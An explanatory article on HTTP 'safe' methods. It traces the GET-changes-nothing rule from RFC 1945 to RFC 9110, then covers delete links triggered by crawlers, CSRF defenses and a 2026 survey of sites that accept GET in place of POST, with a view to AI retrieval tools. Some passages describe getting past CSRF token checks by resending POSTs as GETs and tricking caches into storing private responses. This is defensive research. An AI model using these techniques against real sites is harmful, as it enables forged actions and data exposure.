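# Read-only web requests: the rule that GET should change nothing, how it fails, and what that means for AI retrieval tools

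## What the HTTP standard means by a safe request

The Hypertext Transfer Protocol (HTTP) is the set of rules programs use to request and deliver pages on the World Wide Web. Every HTTP request begins with a word, called the method, that indicates what operation the sender wants. The most familiar method is GET, which a browser sends whenever someone opens a link. Under the HTTP standard, a GET is a request to read, and a site should not delete, buy, subscribe to or confirm anything in response. The standard defines such methods as "safe".

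Much software relies on this rule. Search-engine crawlers open links in bulk, browsers load some pages before anyone clicks, and AI systems with a retrieval tool (a function for searching the web or opening pages) open addresses that no person has looked at. None of these programs can examine a site's code beforehand. Nothing in HTTP stops a site from deleting a record when it receives a GET request, and some sites do. The claim that a program "only reads" because it sends only GET requests therefore depends on sites following a convention, so the exact terms of that convention matter.

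### One page view and one form

Suppose a reader opens a link to `example.org/articles/42`. The browser is the client, the program that sends requests. The program at the other end, which holds the site and replies, is the server. The address is a URL (the standards use a slightly broader term, URI). It consists of a host, `example.org`, and a path, `/articles/42`, and it could also end in a query string, a question mark followed by named values such as `?page=2`. The browser sends the server a short text, of which the essential lines are these:

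```
GET /articles/42 HTTP/1.1
Host: example.org
```

The server returns a status code, 200 if the request succeeded, and then the page. HEAD is a variant of GET in which the server returns only the descriptive lines at the top of the response. A link checker can use it to find out whether an address still works without downloading the page.

Below the article is a comment form. The reader types two words and presses the button, and now the browser sends something different:

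```
POST /articles/42/comments HTTP/1.1
Host: example.org
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded

text=I+disagree
```

POST sends data for the server to process in whatever way the site's programmers have decided. Here, the server stores the reader's new comment. The comment's text is in the body of the request, after the blank line, not in the URL.

Forms can also use GET. A search box normally does, which puts the search terms in the query string and gives the results page an address that people can bookmark or share. A plain link, however, cannot send a POST without JavaScript, as the software consultancy thoughtbot points out. A developer who wants a "delete" link beside each article therefore gets a GET by default and has to do extra work to use another method.

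### From "should never" to "essentially read-only"

The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which standardises internet protocols, publishes its specifications in a numbered series called Requests for Comments (RFCs). RFC 1945, the 1996 description of HTTP/1.0, already had a passage on safe methods, which the online encyclopedia Connected reprints on its page *Safe Methods*. The passage says that, by convention, GET and HEAD "should never have the significance of taking an action other than retrieval". It acknowledges that nobody can ensure a server produces no side effects, and that some sites regard side effects as a feature. The important point, it says, is that the user did not request those effects and so cannot be held accountable for them. RFC 2068, the first HTTP/1.1 specification (1997), kept "should never". In Connected's copy, the only substantive change is that PUT and DELETE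 join POST as examples of methods that a browser can present differently, so that the user notices something may happen.

The 1999 revision, RFC 2616 (Fielding, *Hypertext Transfer Protocol*), softened "should never" to "SHOULD NOT". RFC 2119, published in March 1997, defines such capitalized terms for IETF specifications, and its definition of "SHOULD NOT" allows that "there may exist valid reasons" for an exception. Willison (2005) compared the two documents in *Fighting RFCs with RFCs*, when prefetching software began to trigger delete links. A developer could read the new wording as a loophole, but it was a narrow one. The revision kept the sentence about accountability unchanged, so a developer with a valid reason to delete something in response to a GET request still could not blame the visitor.

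In 2014, RFC 7231 turned the convention into a definition, which the current standard, RFC 9110, keeps. *HTTP Semantics*, as that standard is titled (Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke, 2022), calls a method safe if its defined semantics are "essentially read-only", meaning that the client does not request, and does not expect, any state change on the server (a lasting change in what the server stores). GET and HEAD are safe, as are two diagnostic methods, OPTIONS and TRACE. The standard adds that reasonable use of a safe method is not expected to cause "harm, loss of property, or unusual burden".

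RFC 9110 excuses "the client" where the older texts excused "the user", a change that has turned out to be useful for automated software. In July 1996, people on a mailing list for robot authors were arguing over a crawler's visits to a preprint server at Los Alamos. Some held that if a robot ignores a site's posted instructions for robots, its author is responsible for whatever its requests set off. Simon (1996), in *Safe Methods*, replied by quoting RFC 1945, but he had to interpret a sentence about users as covering programs running unattended. The modern wording covers such programs directly, though only for "reasonable use", so a crawler that floods a small site with requests cannot use the definition as a defense.

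### What the sender asks for and what the server does

The standard defines a safe request by its "semantics", or what the request means. Fielding and colleagues explain that a protocol like HTTP "cannot be defined in terms of what occurs behind the interface", so a specification can define only the form of messages, the intent behind them and how recipients should behave. A request is safe if the sender is asking only for information. The people who run the server are responsible for anything else it does.

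The HTTP standard gives two examples of side effects that a safe request may have. Most servers write a line to a log file after every request, which counts as safe even though the log might fill the disk and bring the server down. Selecting an advertisement also counts as safe, even though it often charges the advertiser's account.

Popular summaries tend to overstate the rule. MDN's *Safe (HTTP Methods)*, from a widely used reference for web developers, first calls a method safe if it "doesn't alter the state of the server" and only later allows for logs and statistics. The consultancy thoughtbot summarizes the rule as "GET requests don't have side effects." Both are good advice for someone building a site, but too strong as descriptions of what a visitor can count on.

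In a public debate in September 1996, a developer named Mike Meyer told the HTTP working group that he routinely built applications in which repeating a GET had further effects, for audiences he controlled. Fielding (1996), a principal author of the specification, replied that Meyer was then accepting personal responsibility for any loss that followed from a misunderstanding or from ordinary automated processes. He wrote that the passage on safe methods sounds like legalese "precisely because it is legalese". He also made a stronger, practical argument that a client must know whether a request is safe before sending it, because a warning in the response comes too late.

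Larry Masinter, another veteran of the working group, took the other side. He argued that the method did not determine whether a request was safe, because the server was "the final arbiter", and that most of the cases the group had examined needed the information only afterwards (Masinter, 2002). He pointed to an experimental header with which a server could label its responses as safe or unsafe to repeat. The header supports his argument less than it seems to, because servers could not use it to declare a GET unsafe. Holtman, in *The Safe Response Header Field*, specified that browsers should ignore a "Safe: no" label on the response to a GET, on the ground that GET is safe by definition.

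Four days after Masinter's message, Fielding (2002) wrote that HTTP requires the semantics of a GET to be safe, not its results, a position RFC 9110 still reflects. If a GET causes someone to lose property, including money, he held the implementation at fault, not the user. A few days later, Joshua Allen of Microsoft proposed adding a sentence to discourage systems from relying on GET being safe. Nottingham (2002) asked how caching and crawling would then work at all.

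Masinter was right that only the server's code determines what a request does. But a crawler has to judge whether a request is safe before sending it, and the method is the only part of the request with an agreed meaning. If GET carried no presumption of safety, the crawler would have to stop or risk changing something on the server. Fielding and colleagues give two purposes for distinguishing safe methods from unsafe ones. The distinction lets crawlers and prefetching "work without fear of causing harm", and it lets browsers and similar programs restrict the automatic use of unsafe methods when handling untrusted content.

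Site owners are responsible for applying this rule. The HTTP standard notes that content-editing software often puts actions into the query string, as in `page?do=delete`. If a URL's purpose is to perform an unsafe action, its owner "MUST disable or disallow that action" when the request uses a safe method. "MUST" is the strongest requirement term in RFCs, so the rule, which looked weaker in 1999, is now stricter than it has ever been for this case. An owner can comply by answering the GET with a page that has a confirmation button, and deleting only when the button sends a POST. No one checks that owners comply, and web server software passes a GET to the application behind it and, as MDN notes, cannot enforce safety by itself.

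### Links and obligations

The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), the other main standards body for the web, reached a similar rule by considering what users commit to when they follow a link. Its Technical Architecture Group (TAG) documents general principles of the web's design. The group's March 2004 finding, *URIs, Addressability, and the use of HTTP GET and POST* (Jacobs, 2004), states that "agents do not incur obligations by following links". Agents here include software. A notice reading "by following this link you accept our terms" therefore binds nobody, since anyone can publish another link to the same page, and people who use that link will never have seen the notice. Developers should use GET when the interaction resembles a question, and POST when it resembles an order, changes something in a way the user would perceive, or has a result the user should be accountable for.

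Jacobs illustrated this with a mailing list. Someone asks to join and receives an email with a confirmation link. In the faulty design, opening the link completes the subscription, so a mail program that fetches links in advance signs its user up without their knowledge. In the correct design, the link opens a page with a "Confirm" button that sends a POST request. Jacobs blamed the server for an unwanted subscription and considered mail programs free to follow links.

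The same finding classes a visitor counter as safe. The number on the server goes up with each visit, but visitors commit themselves to nothing. Noah Mendelsohn, then at IBM, disagreed, and there was some hesitation on the point during drafting. A draft by Jacobs (2003), dated 16 September, listed interactions with "an audited resource", one whose owner keeps track of access, as unsafe. Jacobs had added the example at Mendelsohn's suggestion but admitted in the covering message, *Updated finding* (2003), to being unsure what "audited" meant. The W3C's announcement list for September 2003 records the finding as accepted on the 22nd, the day before the date on Mendelsohn's objection.

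Mendelsohn (2003) argued that safety cannot depend only on consequences for the user, because the owner of a resource decides which operations are safe. An owner may well want a consequence when someone looks up sensitive information, or may need a reliable count of clicks, and should use POST in those cases. Mendelsohn also objected that the TAG had tied GET to the absence of an obligation, whereas POST is defined by changes of state, and these are "apples and oranges". If GET is for whatever creates no obligation, then it follows, absurdly, that a developer should use it even for an update to server data that creates no obligation.

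The logical point counts against the TAG's slogan. It counts less against the TAG's checklist, which mentions perceptible changes separately, and not at all against RFC 9110, where the test is whether the client requests a state change. Mendelsohn's case on counters is weaker. When a cache serves a stored copy of a page, the server never learns of the visit and the count comes out low. An owner can forbid stored copies with a header called Cache-Control, as Fielding had observed in 1996, and keep using GET. Moving every audited page to POST would stop readers from bookmarking or linking to it. With GET, though, the owner can't be sure that each request came from a person rather than a crawler or a prefetching browser. The objection is not reflected in the March 2004 version of the text, which still lists the counter among its safe examples and no longer mentions audited resources.

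### Safe, idempotent, cacheable

People often confuse safety with idempotence, as the web's designers did at first. While RFC 2616 was still a draft, Connolly, of the W3C, remarked that what used to be "(erroneously) called idempotent" was now called "safe". A request is idempotent if sending it several times has the same intended effect as sending it once. Let *s* be what the server stores and *f*(*s*) what it would store if it did exactly what the client asked. Log entries don't count as part of *f*, because the client didn't ask for them. A method is safe if *f*(*s*) = *s*, and idempotent if *f*(*f*(*s*)) = *f*(*s*), so every safe method is idempotent. Deletion is idempotent but not safe, because a request to delete article 42 removes it and repeating the request changes nothing further. Posting a comment is usually neither, because sending the request twice leaves two comments.

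If a connection drops before the response arrives, a client can repeat an idempotent request whether or not the original got through. RFC 2616 notes that this guarantee covers only single requests. If a program reads a number with GET and writes back that number plus one with PUT, each request is idempotent, but running the pair twice adds two.

Cacheability is a third property. A response is cacheable if a browser or an intermediary may store it and use it to answer a later request, which then never reaches the site.

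| Method | What the client asks for | Safe | Idempotent | Cacheable |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GET | the page at an address | yes | yes | yes |
| HEAD | the same, without the content | yes | yes | yes |
| OPTIONS | which methods an address accepts | yes | yes | no |
| QUERY | the result of a query sent in the body | yes | yes | yes |
| PUT | replacement of what is at an address | no | yes | no |
| DELETE | removal of what is at an address | no | yes | no |
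| POST | processing of submitted data | not in general | not in general | only under conditions, and only for later GET or HEAD requests |

The new QUERY method is for requests that only read but carry too much data for a URL. For example, a service that checks an uploaded document for errors changes nothing, but it receives the document by POST, so the client "has no way to know that it's safe" (Connolly, 2003). According to Jacobs, engineers discussed a QUERY method or a "safe POST" at an IETF meeting in December 1996 but reached no agreement.

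Agreement took almost thirty years. According to the IETF's page for *The HTTP QUERY Method* (2026), RFC 10008 was published on 15 June 2026. It makes QUERY a Proposed Standard, the lower of the two grades on the IETF's standards track. RFC 9110 has been an Internet Standard, the higher grade, since the RFC Editor (2022) announced it. InfoQ (2026) reports that QUERY is the first new standard method since PATCH in 2010, and widespread adoption will probably take years.

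A request can be safe even if the server creates a new resource while handling it. *The HTTP QUERY Method*, by Reschke, Snell and Bishop, allows a server to store the result of a query and give it its own address. In one example, a search of a contact list produces a new resource at `/contacts/stored-results/17`, which later GET requests can retrieve. The QUERY is still safe because the client did not ask for any change to the contact list, and the server created the extra resource without being asked.

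### Four requests

Take a news site on which a logged-in editor opens four links, one after another. The browser sends:

```
GET /articles/42
GET /articles/43
GET /click?ad=7
GET /articles/42?do=delete
```

The first request retrieves an article. The server adds a line to its log and returns the page. This is as close to pure reading as a web request gets, and every version of the rule allows it.

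Article 43 displays its view count, so the server also adds one to a stored total when the editor's browser requests the page. Under RFC 9110 the request is safe because the browser requested the article, not the increase, and the TAG's finding explicitly covers this case. Mendelsohn would call the request unsafe if the site's owner needed the total to be reliable.

Opening the advertisement costs the advertiser money. RFC 9110 defines a safe request as one not expected to cause loss of property, yet it lists an advertising charge as an acceptable side effect. One possible explanation is that the advertiser agreed in advance, with the site or an advertising network, to pay for clicks. The editor who clicked had no part in that agreement and asked only to see the page behind the advertisement. So the request is safe, and any dispute over charges for clicks that no customer made is between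 the advertiser and whoever billed for them.

Following the last link deletes the article. Deletion is the purpose of that address, not a by-product of retrieval, and the owner has failed in the duty to disable such actions when the request uses a safe method. This is an unsafe GET, a GET request that violates the standard by causing a state change someone would care about. The editor's browser worked correctly, and so would a crawler that followed the same link with the editor's permissions. Neither could tell from the address that the request would delete the article. A person might take `do=delete` as a warning, but HTTP gives those characters no meaning, and another site could put the same deletion behind an address like `/r/8841`.

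## How opening a link can change something on a server

When a request reaches a site, the site's application picks a piece of code, called a handler, to deal with it. *When POST Becomes GET* (Golinelli, Hannachi and Crispo, 2026) points out that many frameworks (ready-made foundations for web applications) choose the handler mainly by the path in the address. If the handler for `/notes/42/delete` removes a row from a database without checking the request's method, it removes the row whether the request uses GET or POST.

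In the HTTP standard, Fielding and colleagues write that a method ought to mean the same thing everywhere, but they acknowledge that each resource "determines for itself whether those semantics are implemented or allowed". They also warn against thinking of a path as a file name. The address may lead to a file, but it may equally lead to a program that the server runs with the request as its input.

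### Delete buttons that are really links

García Isaía (2023) describes a site with a page of retailers and a DELETE button next to each one. The buttons were ordinary links, and opening one removed that retailer from the database. The site also had a plugin that opened every link on a page to check that it was valid, so each check of that page deleted every retailer listed on it. The buttons had worked well enough for people who clicked them, and the plugin was working as intended. RFC 9110 predicts this kind of accident. Link maintenance is the first item in its list of automated processes that will cause "unfortunate side effects" on such sites.

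Developers had reasons for building delete links. *The Expectations of Links*, on snook.ca, argues that links are small, unobtrusive and familiar. Frameworks such as Ruby on Rails also encouraged tidy addresses like `/email/190/delete`. Just after the online organizer Backpack switched its own links to POST, the creator of Rails agreed on dhh.dk that POST was the better way to modify data. He blamed HTML for the habit and said that people "route around specs" that stop them from doing what they need to do. Brocklehurst (2015), in *HTTP Safety Doesn't Happen by Accident*, notes that a style sheet can make a button look like a link, so a developer who wants a discreet "delete" no longer has to use GET.

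Links that cancel an order or approve a comment work the same way. Marking mail as read is a less clear-cut case. A commenter on the programmer Ian Bicking's blog observed that reading mail is a kind of GET, yet mail sites mark a message as read when the user opens it. The commenter asked how a site could tell a person from a robot before changing that mark. A site cannot do so reliably, but wrongly marking a message as read does much less harm than losing an address book.

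### One link, opened by a person and by a program

Suppose a note-taking site puts this link beside note 42:

```
<a href="/notes/42/delete"
   onclick="return confirm('Delete this note?')">Delete</a>
```

The `href` part holds the address. The `onclick` part holds a line of JavaScript, which the browser runs when someone clicks. A person clicks, and a box appears with the buttons OK and Cancel. If the person chooses Cancel, the JavaScript tells the browser not to follow the link, and no request leaves the computer. If the person chooses OK, the browser sends this:

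```
GET /notes/42/delete HTTP/1.1
Host: example.org
Cookie: SID=31d4d96e407aad42
```

The last line identifies the logged-in user. The handler checks that this user owns the note, deletes it and returns the remaining list.

Later a link checker, using the same person's login, downloads the same page's HTML, collects every `href` and requests each address in turn. It runs no JavaScript, so it ignores the `onclick` line. Its request for `/notes/42/delete` has the same method, path and cookie as the person's, none of which records whether anyone answered a question first. The handler deletes note 42, then notes 43 and 44 when the checker requests their links.

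Even a program that can run JavaScript may not trigger the confirmation box, because the box appears in response to a click, and software that loads an address in advance does not click on anything. Willison noticed this in 2005, when preloading software was getting past confirmation prompts that developers had carefully added.

The snook.ca article defends such prompts on the grounds that people also press the wrong thing by accident, whether it is a link or a form button. A confirmation box does help with those mistakes, but a box that exists only in the browser doesn't address automated requests.

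The repair replaces the link with a form:

```
<form action="/notes/42/delete" method="post">
  <input type="hidden" name="csrf_token" value="(random value)">
  <button>Delete</button>
</form>
```

The page now has no `href` for a link checker to collect, and pressing the button sends a POST. The hidden field guards against a separate danger, requests from other sites. The developer can keep the confirmation box. The handler must also change so that it deletes only on a POST. It can reply to a GET with status 405, "Method Not Allowed", which means that the server recognizes the method but does not permit it at that address. After a successful deletion, it can reply with status 303, which sends the browser to the list of notes with a new GET.

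Changing the page but not the handler doesn't fix the fault. The old address would still delete the note if someone opened it from a bookmark or a program followed it from a saved copy of the page.

Another fix is to keep the link but have it open a confirmation page, where a button sends the POST. A commenter on Bicking's blog proposed this, and someone replied that some deletions are minor or easy to undo and don't need an extra step. That is a reasonable objection to the confirmation page, but POST doesn't require one, since the form above deletes with a single press.

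Rails offered a third arrangement, in which the `link_to` helper can produce something that looks like a link but uses JavaScript to build and submit a form when someone clicks it. *Delete/put links break your Rails app* criticizes this because, for visitors without JavaScript, the "Delete Image" link merely opens the image's own page. That is a nuisance for those visitors, but it is the right way to fail, because a crawler that follows the link deletes nothing. By contrast, the note link above loses its safeguard without JavaScript but still takes effect. Brocklehurst prefers the plainer `button_to`, which shows people that they are about to do something.

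### The cookie that makes the request count

A stranger who opens `/notes/42/delete` should get a login page. The server deletes the note only when the request carries the user's authority, which on most sites comes from a session cookie.

HTTP by itself does not connect one request with the next, so when someone logs in, the server's response includes a short token that the browser returns with later requests to the same site. The line `SID=31d4d96e407aad42` in the example comes from *Cookies* (Bingler, West and Wilander, 2025), the current revision of the cookie specification, which the IETF's steering group approved as a Proposed Standard on 2 December 2025 (IESG, *Protocol Action*, 2025). The browser attaches the token automatically, according to rules about the address and the context, and the server then treats the request as the user's own.

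The same unsafe GET request can be harmless or destructive depending on which software sends it. If the note-taking site's handler checks for a login, a public search crawler can't delete anyone's notes, because it isn't logged in. A browser extension, or any other program working inside a logged-in browser, can delete anything the user could.

Logout links are a common example. Opening `/logout` sends a request to end the session that the cookie identifies. Little is lost, and a second visit changes nothing further, but ending the login is still a lasting change, and a program that follows every link on a page will log itself out partway through. When Golinelli and colleagues built a crawler to study live sites, they had it drop requests whose paths suggested logging out, along with potentially destructive requests. They explain that even without an account, signing out can invalidate a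 temporary session and disrupt the rest of the crawl.

### Addresses that carry their own authority

Some links work without a cookie. To check an email address, a site sends a message containing a link such as `example.org/confirm?token=...`, which ends in a long random value. Only someone who can read the message should know that value, so the site treats whoever opens the link as the owner of the mailbox. Unsubscribe links and one-time login links often work the same way.

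The design suits email because the recipient may open the message on a phone that has never logged in to the site. A link in a message also cannot send a POST, since mail programs generally do not run the JavaScript it would need, so the developer has to start with a GET. The fault occurs when the handler treats that first GET as the recipient's decision.

The harm depends on what the link does. Confirmation links fail as in Jacobs's mailing-list example. If software opens an unsubscribe link, the reader stops getting messages and may not notice for weeks. If it opens a one-time login link, the software gets the session and the link stops working, so the person who clicks a minute later finds it expired. Mail scanners can cause all of these failures because they open links to look for malicious pages.

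When a server relies on cookies for authority, a program can protect itself and its user by having none. This doesn't help when the link itself carries the authority, because the program supplies it just by requesting the address. Jacobs's remedy, a page with a "Confirm" button, also works for login links if the server leaves the token unused until someone presses the button, though this adds a step for the user.

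### Handlers that accept either method

A site can also end up with an unsafe GET by accident, when its developers build a proper POST form but the handler behind it never checks the method. Suppose the form sends a POST to `/notes/delete` with `id=42` in the body. If the server also accepts a GET for `/notes/delete?id=42` and responds equivalently, it has what Golinelli and colleagues call method interchangeability. This is often harmless. A search page may accept both methods on purpose, and an equivalent response does not prove that anything changed on the server.

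To find out whether frameworks encourage this behavior, Golinelli and colleagues examined a range of frameworks from seven language and platform ecosystems. They read the official documentation and built small test applications to see whether a GET with the same inputs could reach a handler meant for POST. They found that it matters whether the framework gives the developer data from the address and the body through a single interface and, separately, whether a handler accepts every method unless the developer restricts it.

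| Framework | Data from the address and the body | Methods that reach a handler |
|---|---|---|
| Plain PHP | merged in `$_REQUEST` | any, unless the script checks |
| Spring MVC | one interface for address and form data, JSON separate | any with a generic mapping, one with a specific mapping |
| ASP.NET Core | can draw on several sources, developer can name one | any with a generic route, one with a specific attribute |
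| Rails, Laravel | merged, including JSON | both GET and POST only if the developer sets that up |
| Flask | merged in `request.values`, JSON separate | both GET and POST only if the developer sets that up |
| Django | separate | any, unless the developer restricts the handler |
| Express, FastAPI, NestJS, Next.js, SvelteKit | separate | interchange takes deliberate choices by the developer |

Plain PHP is the clearest case, because a script that reads its input from `$_REQUEST` without checking the method will treat a GET and a POST with the same data alike. Spring and ASP.NET Core behave similarly only in some configurations, and mainly for form data. Rails, Laravel and Flask make the data look the same to a handler that serves both methods, but the developer has to set the handler to accept both.

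In Django, keeping the data apart gives only partial protection. A handler that looks for `id` in the form data will not find it in a GET. But if the number is in the path, as in `/notes/42/delete`, the handler needs no form data and will delete the note on a GET unless the developer restricts which methods it accepts. Django provides a decorator for this, which is a line placed above the handler's code.

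The analysis concerns accidents and was not meant to find flaws in particular frameworks. A careful default makes it harder to expose a POST handler to GET by mistake, but none of these frameworks stops a developer from deliberately writing a GET handler that deletes data, as the builders of the retailers page did. An HTML form also sends a GET by default, so if a developer forgets `method="post"` and the handler accepts both methods, the form appears to work and the mistake can go unnoticed.

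A request's method can also change on the way to the handler. The server software Nginx can be set to replace the method when it forwards a request. Some frameworks support "method override", which lets a request sent as GET appear to the application as a POST, as MDN's *Cross-site request forgery (CSRF)* warns. A handler that accepts only POST can then run in response to a GET.

### Interfaces with rules of their own

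Programs often exchange data with a site through an interface that uses one address for all requests. GraphQL, a widely used query language for such interfaces, uses queries to read data and mutations to write it. A client might send both to `/graphql`, so the path doesn't show whether a request reads or writes. Under the draft standard for GraphQL over HTTP, a server must accept queries by POST and may accept them by GET, but must not execute a mutation by GET. GraphQL's *Serving over HTTP* gives developers the same instruction.

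Golinelli and colleagues found similar divisions between GET and POST elsewhere. SPARQL, a query language for linked data, allows queries by GET or POST but updates only by POST. OData, a protocol for data services, uses GET for functions, which must have no side effects, and POST for actions, which may have them.

These rules are more precise than the general one for GET because the server can tell from the request whether it is a read or a write, and can refuse writes sent by GET, though developers still have to program it to do so. The GraphQL component of Responder, a web framework for Python, "executed whatever operation arrived", including mutations sent by GET, until a security audit found the problem and it was fixed.

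### Why defenses against forged requests let GET through

In cross-site request forgery (CSRF), one site makes a visitor's browser send an unwanted request to another site where the visitor is logged in. The browser attaches the visitor's cookies automatically, so the attack works without the attacker ever seeing them. In *Cross-Site Request Forgery*, Valsorda (2025) describes the attacker as borrowing the cookies' "ambient authority", meaning authority that goes along with a request regardless of who started it.

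Using POST does not prevent this by itself, because a page on one site can submit a form to another. The usual defense is a token like the hidden field in the repaired form. The server puts an unpredictable value in its own page and acts only if the request includes that value. Another site normally can't read the page, so it can't supply the value. A newer defense checks the `Sec-Fetch-Site` header, which the browser sets to show whether a request came from the same site or a different one.

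Both defenses normally allow GET requests. Valsorda's recommended procedure begins by allowing all GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests, since other layers already rely on those methods changing nothing. The Go programming language's standard library (2025) follows that procedure. Its code approves a GET before checking where the request came from, and a comment warns developers not to change state in response to safe methods.

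Sites can't easily avoid exempting GET requests from the token check, because links from search results, messages and other sites produce GET requests that carry no token. A site that rejected them would block anyone who followed those links. But if a site lets a GET request delete something, that request is exempt too. On two live sites, Golinelli and colleagues found that some requests with an invalid token failed as POST but succeeded as GET.

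Browsers add a further defense through a cookie setting called SameSite, which has a similar exception. With the value Strict, the browser leaves the cookie out of every request that comes from another site. As MDN notes, this means that someone who follows a link from elsewhere arrives looking logged out. The value Lax avoids this by sending the cookie with a request from another site if the request uses a safe method and is a top-level navigation, meaning that it loads a new page in the window rather than, say, an image within a page. An ordinary link meets both conditions, so if it leads to a GET that changes something, the browser sends the cookie and the server makes the change.

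Browser makers tried to make Lax the default for cookies with no SameSite setting, but according to Valsorda the rollout mostly failed because it broke too many sites, particularly their single sign-on systems. Some browsers settled on a version that also sends cookies with unsafe methods. MDN suggests using two cookies, a Lax one for showing pages to logged-in users and a Strict one for authorizing changes. A handler that required the Strict cookie would reject even a GET that changes something if it came from another site.

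These CSRF defenses would not have prevented the deletion of note 42, because they are meant to stop requests that other sites start, and the delete link was on the site's own page. When software preloads the link inside the user's browser, it makes a same-site request, so the browser sends even a Strict cookie. A separate link checker that has the user's cookie typically sends no `Sec-Fetch-Site` header, and Go's code allows requests with neither that header nor the older `Origin` header, on the assumption that they do not come from another site's page. A token in the link would not help either, because a program that copies the address also copies the token.

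## How often real sites break the rule

An outsider can test a site without seeing its code by sending a GET where its pages send a POST and checking the response. Golinelli and colleagues, whose analysis of frameworks explains why this sometimes works, tried it on the 10,000 most popular sites in the 7 May 2026 version of Tranco, a ranking made for researchers. Their 2026 survey is the first large measurement of method interchangeability on live sites, and they found it on 407 sites, or 4.1%.

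That number counts equivalent responses to addresses that the researchers wrote themselves, not the share of sites where opening a link can change something. The evidence about actual changes comes mostly from older and smaller studies.

### Rewriting a POST as a GET

An automated browser visited each site without logging in. It opened at most 10 pages, filled in forms with harmless made-up values and clicked some of the buttons. It recorded the POST requests that these actions triggered and those that scripts sent while pages loaded, stopping after about 100 per site.

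Suppose one of those requests came from a store finder:

```
POST /stores/find HTTP/1.1
Host: example.org
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded

city=Trento&radius=10
```

The researchers' software moved the data from the body into the address and sent two GETs:

```
GET /stores/find?city=Trento&radius=10
GET /stores/find
```

The GET without parameters is a control, because some servers return the same page, perhaps a general error message, whatever the parameters are. If this GET produces the same response as the original POST, a match from the GET with parameters is weak evidence that the server read the city and the radius.

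Golinelli and colleagues treated two responses as equivalent if they had the same status code and a structural similarity of at least 0.95. For web pages, the similarity score compares the sequence of HTML tags and ignores the text between them. For JSON, a common text format for structured data, it compares field names and ignores most values, although different values in a field such as "success" rule out a match. An exact comparison would have been too strict because timestamps and random identifiers differ from one response to the next. However, the looser test can match two pages built from the same template even if one reads "Your message was sent" and the other "Something went wrong".

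Each request then fell into one of four classes:

| Class | GET with parameters matches the POST | GET without parameters matches the POST | Requests |
|---|---|---|---|
| A: strong interchangeability | yes | no | 1,228 (8.6%) |
| B: ambiguous | yes | yes | 1,782 (12.5%) |
| C: baseline collision | no | yes | 242 (1.7%) |
| D: not interchangeable | no | no | 10,992 (77.2%) |

Only class A counts toward the 407 sites. The control put 59% of the 3,010 apparent matches in doubt. Some requests in class B may still be interchangeable. A store finder that shows the same layout for every city, and when no city is given, would fall into class B.

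To check the software, a reviewer examined 60 records by hand, half from class A and half from class D. In all 30 from class A, the rewritten GET had the same outcome as the POST, though in one the control also seemed to match, which would move it to class B. None of the 30 from class D were equivalent. These results are good support for class A but weaker support for class D, which is much larger. If 5% of class D were equivalent, or about 550 requests, a sample of 30 would include none of them about one time in five. The software is therefore more likely to have missed interchangeable requests than to have wrongly labeled many as interchangeable.

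### What the survey found on 407 sites

The browser captured 21,280 POST requests on 3,200 of the 10,000 sites. The software could rewrite and send 14,244 of them, from 2,734 sites. Most of the others carried data in a format the software did not support.

The 407 sites are 4.1% of all sites tested, 12.7% of those where the browser captured a POST, and 14.9% of those where the software could make the comparison. Golinelli and colleagues also counted routes, where a route is roughly one address that receives one kind of POST. They found that 646 of 8,291 routes (7.8%) were interchangeable.

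The 6,800 sites with no captured POST were not tested, so 14.9% is the better estimate of how common interchangeability is among sites that use POST, and 4.1% is a floor. A single request was enough for a site to count toward either figure, so these sites may not ignore the method everywhere.

Most of the interchangeable requests look harmless. The software sorted them by the words in their addresses, parameters and responses, and the largest groups were search or filtering (30.9%) and analytics or tracking (15.1%). But 387 (31.5%) received labels that the researchers call potentially security-relevant, such as authentication, account settings, checkout and content creation. The labels are guesses based on vocabulary, so a request labelled "account settings" may only have redirected an anonymous visitor to a login page.

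Of all the requests that the software rewrote and sent, 32.5% had security-relevant labels, which is almost the same share. If the labels are even roughly right, developers don't check the method more carefully for security-relevant requests than for others.

The researchers also tested whether rewriting a POST as a GET could get around a site's CSRF protection. Of the 1,228 interchangeable requests, 115, on 46 sites, contained something whose name suggested a CSRF token. The researchers resent both the POST and GET versions of each, with the token removed and with it altered. In seven cases, on two sites, the server refused the POST without a valid token but accepted the GET without one.

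Switching to GET avoided the token check in seven of the 115 tests, but most of the other tests had no working check to avoid. In 78 of them, the server accepted invalid tokens with either method. Some of those fields may not have been tokens, since one of the names the researchers searched for was "state", which is also part of many postal addresses. Another 26 tests failed or were inconclusive, three gave mixed results, and in the remaining one the server enforced the token on the GET. So where a token check was clearly working, switching to GET usually avoided it, though two sites are too few to support a general rate.

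Rewriting a POST as a GET can also expose data, because a cache may store a reply meant for one visitor and serve it to another. For 136 of the interchangeable requests, on 50 sites, the response to the rewritten request was cacheable without further changes. For another 56, on nine sites, the researchers got a cache to store the response by making the address look like a style sheet's.

### Why 4.1% is not the risk of opening a page

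An equivalent response does not prove that anything changed. Suppose submitting a contact form normally brings up a page that reads "Thank you for your message", and the rewritten GET brings up the same page. The server may have sent the message again, or it may show that page to anyone who requests the address with the right fields. Golinelli and colleagues could not tell which had happened, and they present none of their cases as confirmed attacks.

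The survey also left out the requests most likely to do damage. The crawler dropped requests with destructive-looking paths and avoided buttons whose labels suggested a state-changing action. It never logged in, so it could not reach the delete buttons and settings pages that only account holders see. These precautions were reasonable on other people's sites, but they mean the survey could miss a site that deletes records in response to a GET. Its results therefore cannot set an upper limit on the number of unsafe GETs.

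Even a perfect count of interchangeable requests would not measure how many dangerous links exist. The researchers' software generated the address `/stores/find?city=Trento&radius=10`, and there may be no link to it anywhere on the web. A crawler that only follows links will not request it unless someone publishes a link to it.

A program that composes addresses, unlike one that only follows links, can send a GET that nobody has published to a handler that the developer thought only a button could reach. It might read a form, put its own values into a query string and request the result, or it might guess an address from the pattern of others it has seen. Interchangeability therefore adds to what its requests might do. A link-following crawler mainly faces the older danger of delete links like the ones on García Isaía's page of retailers, and the survey did not look for those.

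The separation is incomplete because anyone can publish a composed address as a link. An attacker would do this to target a logged-in visitor, and a crawler could find the same link.

### Requests that people labelled by hand

To train software that detects CSRF weaknesses, Calzavara, Conti and colleagues (2019), in *Mitch*, opened accounts on 60 popular sites. They used functions such as liking a post or editing a profile, and recorded the requests that each click produced. Two of the researchers then labelled a request as sensitive if it made a security-relevant change under the user's login and the effect was visible in the browser. This definition excludes log entries and tracking, so it comes close to the kind of state change that someone would care about.

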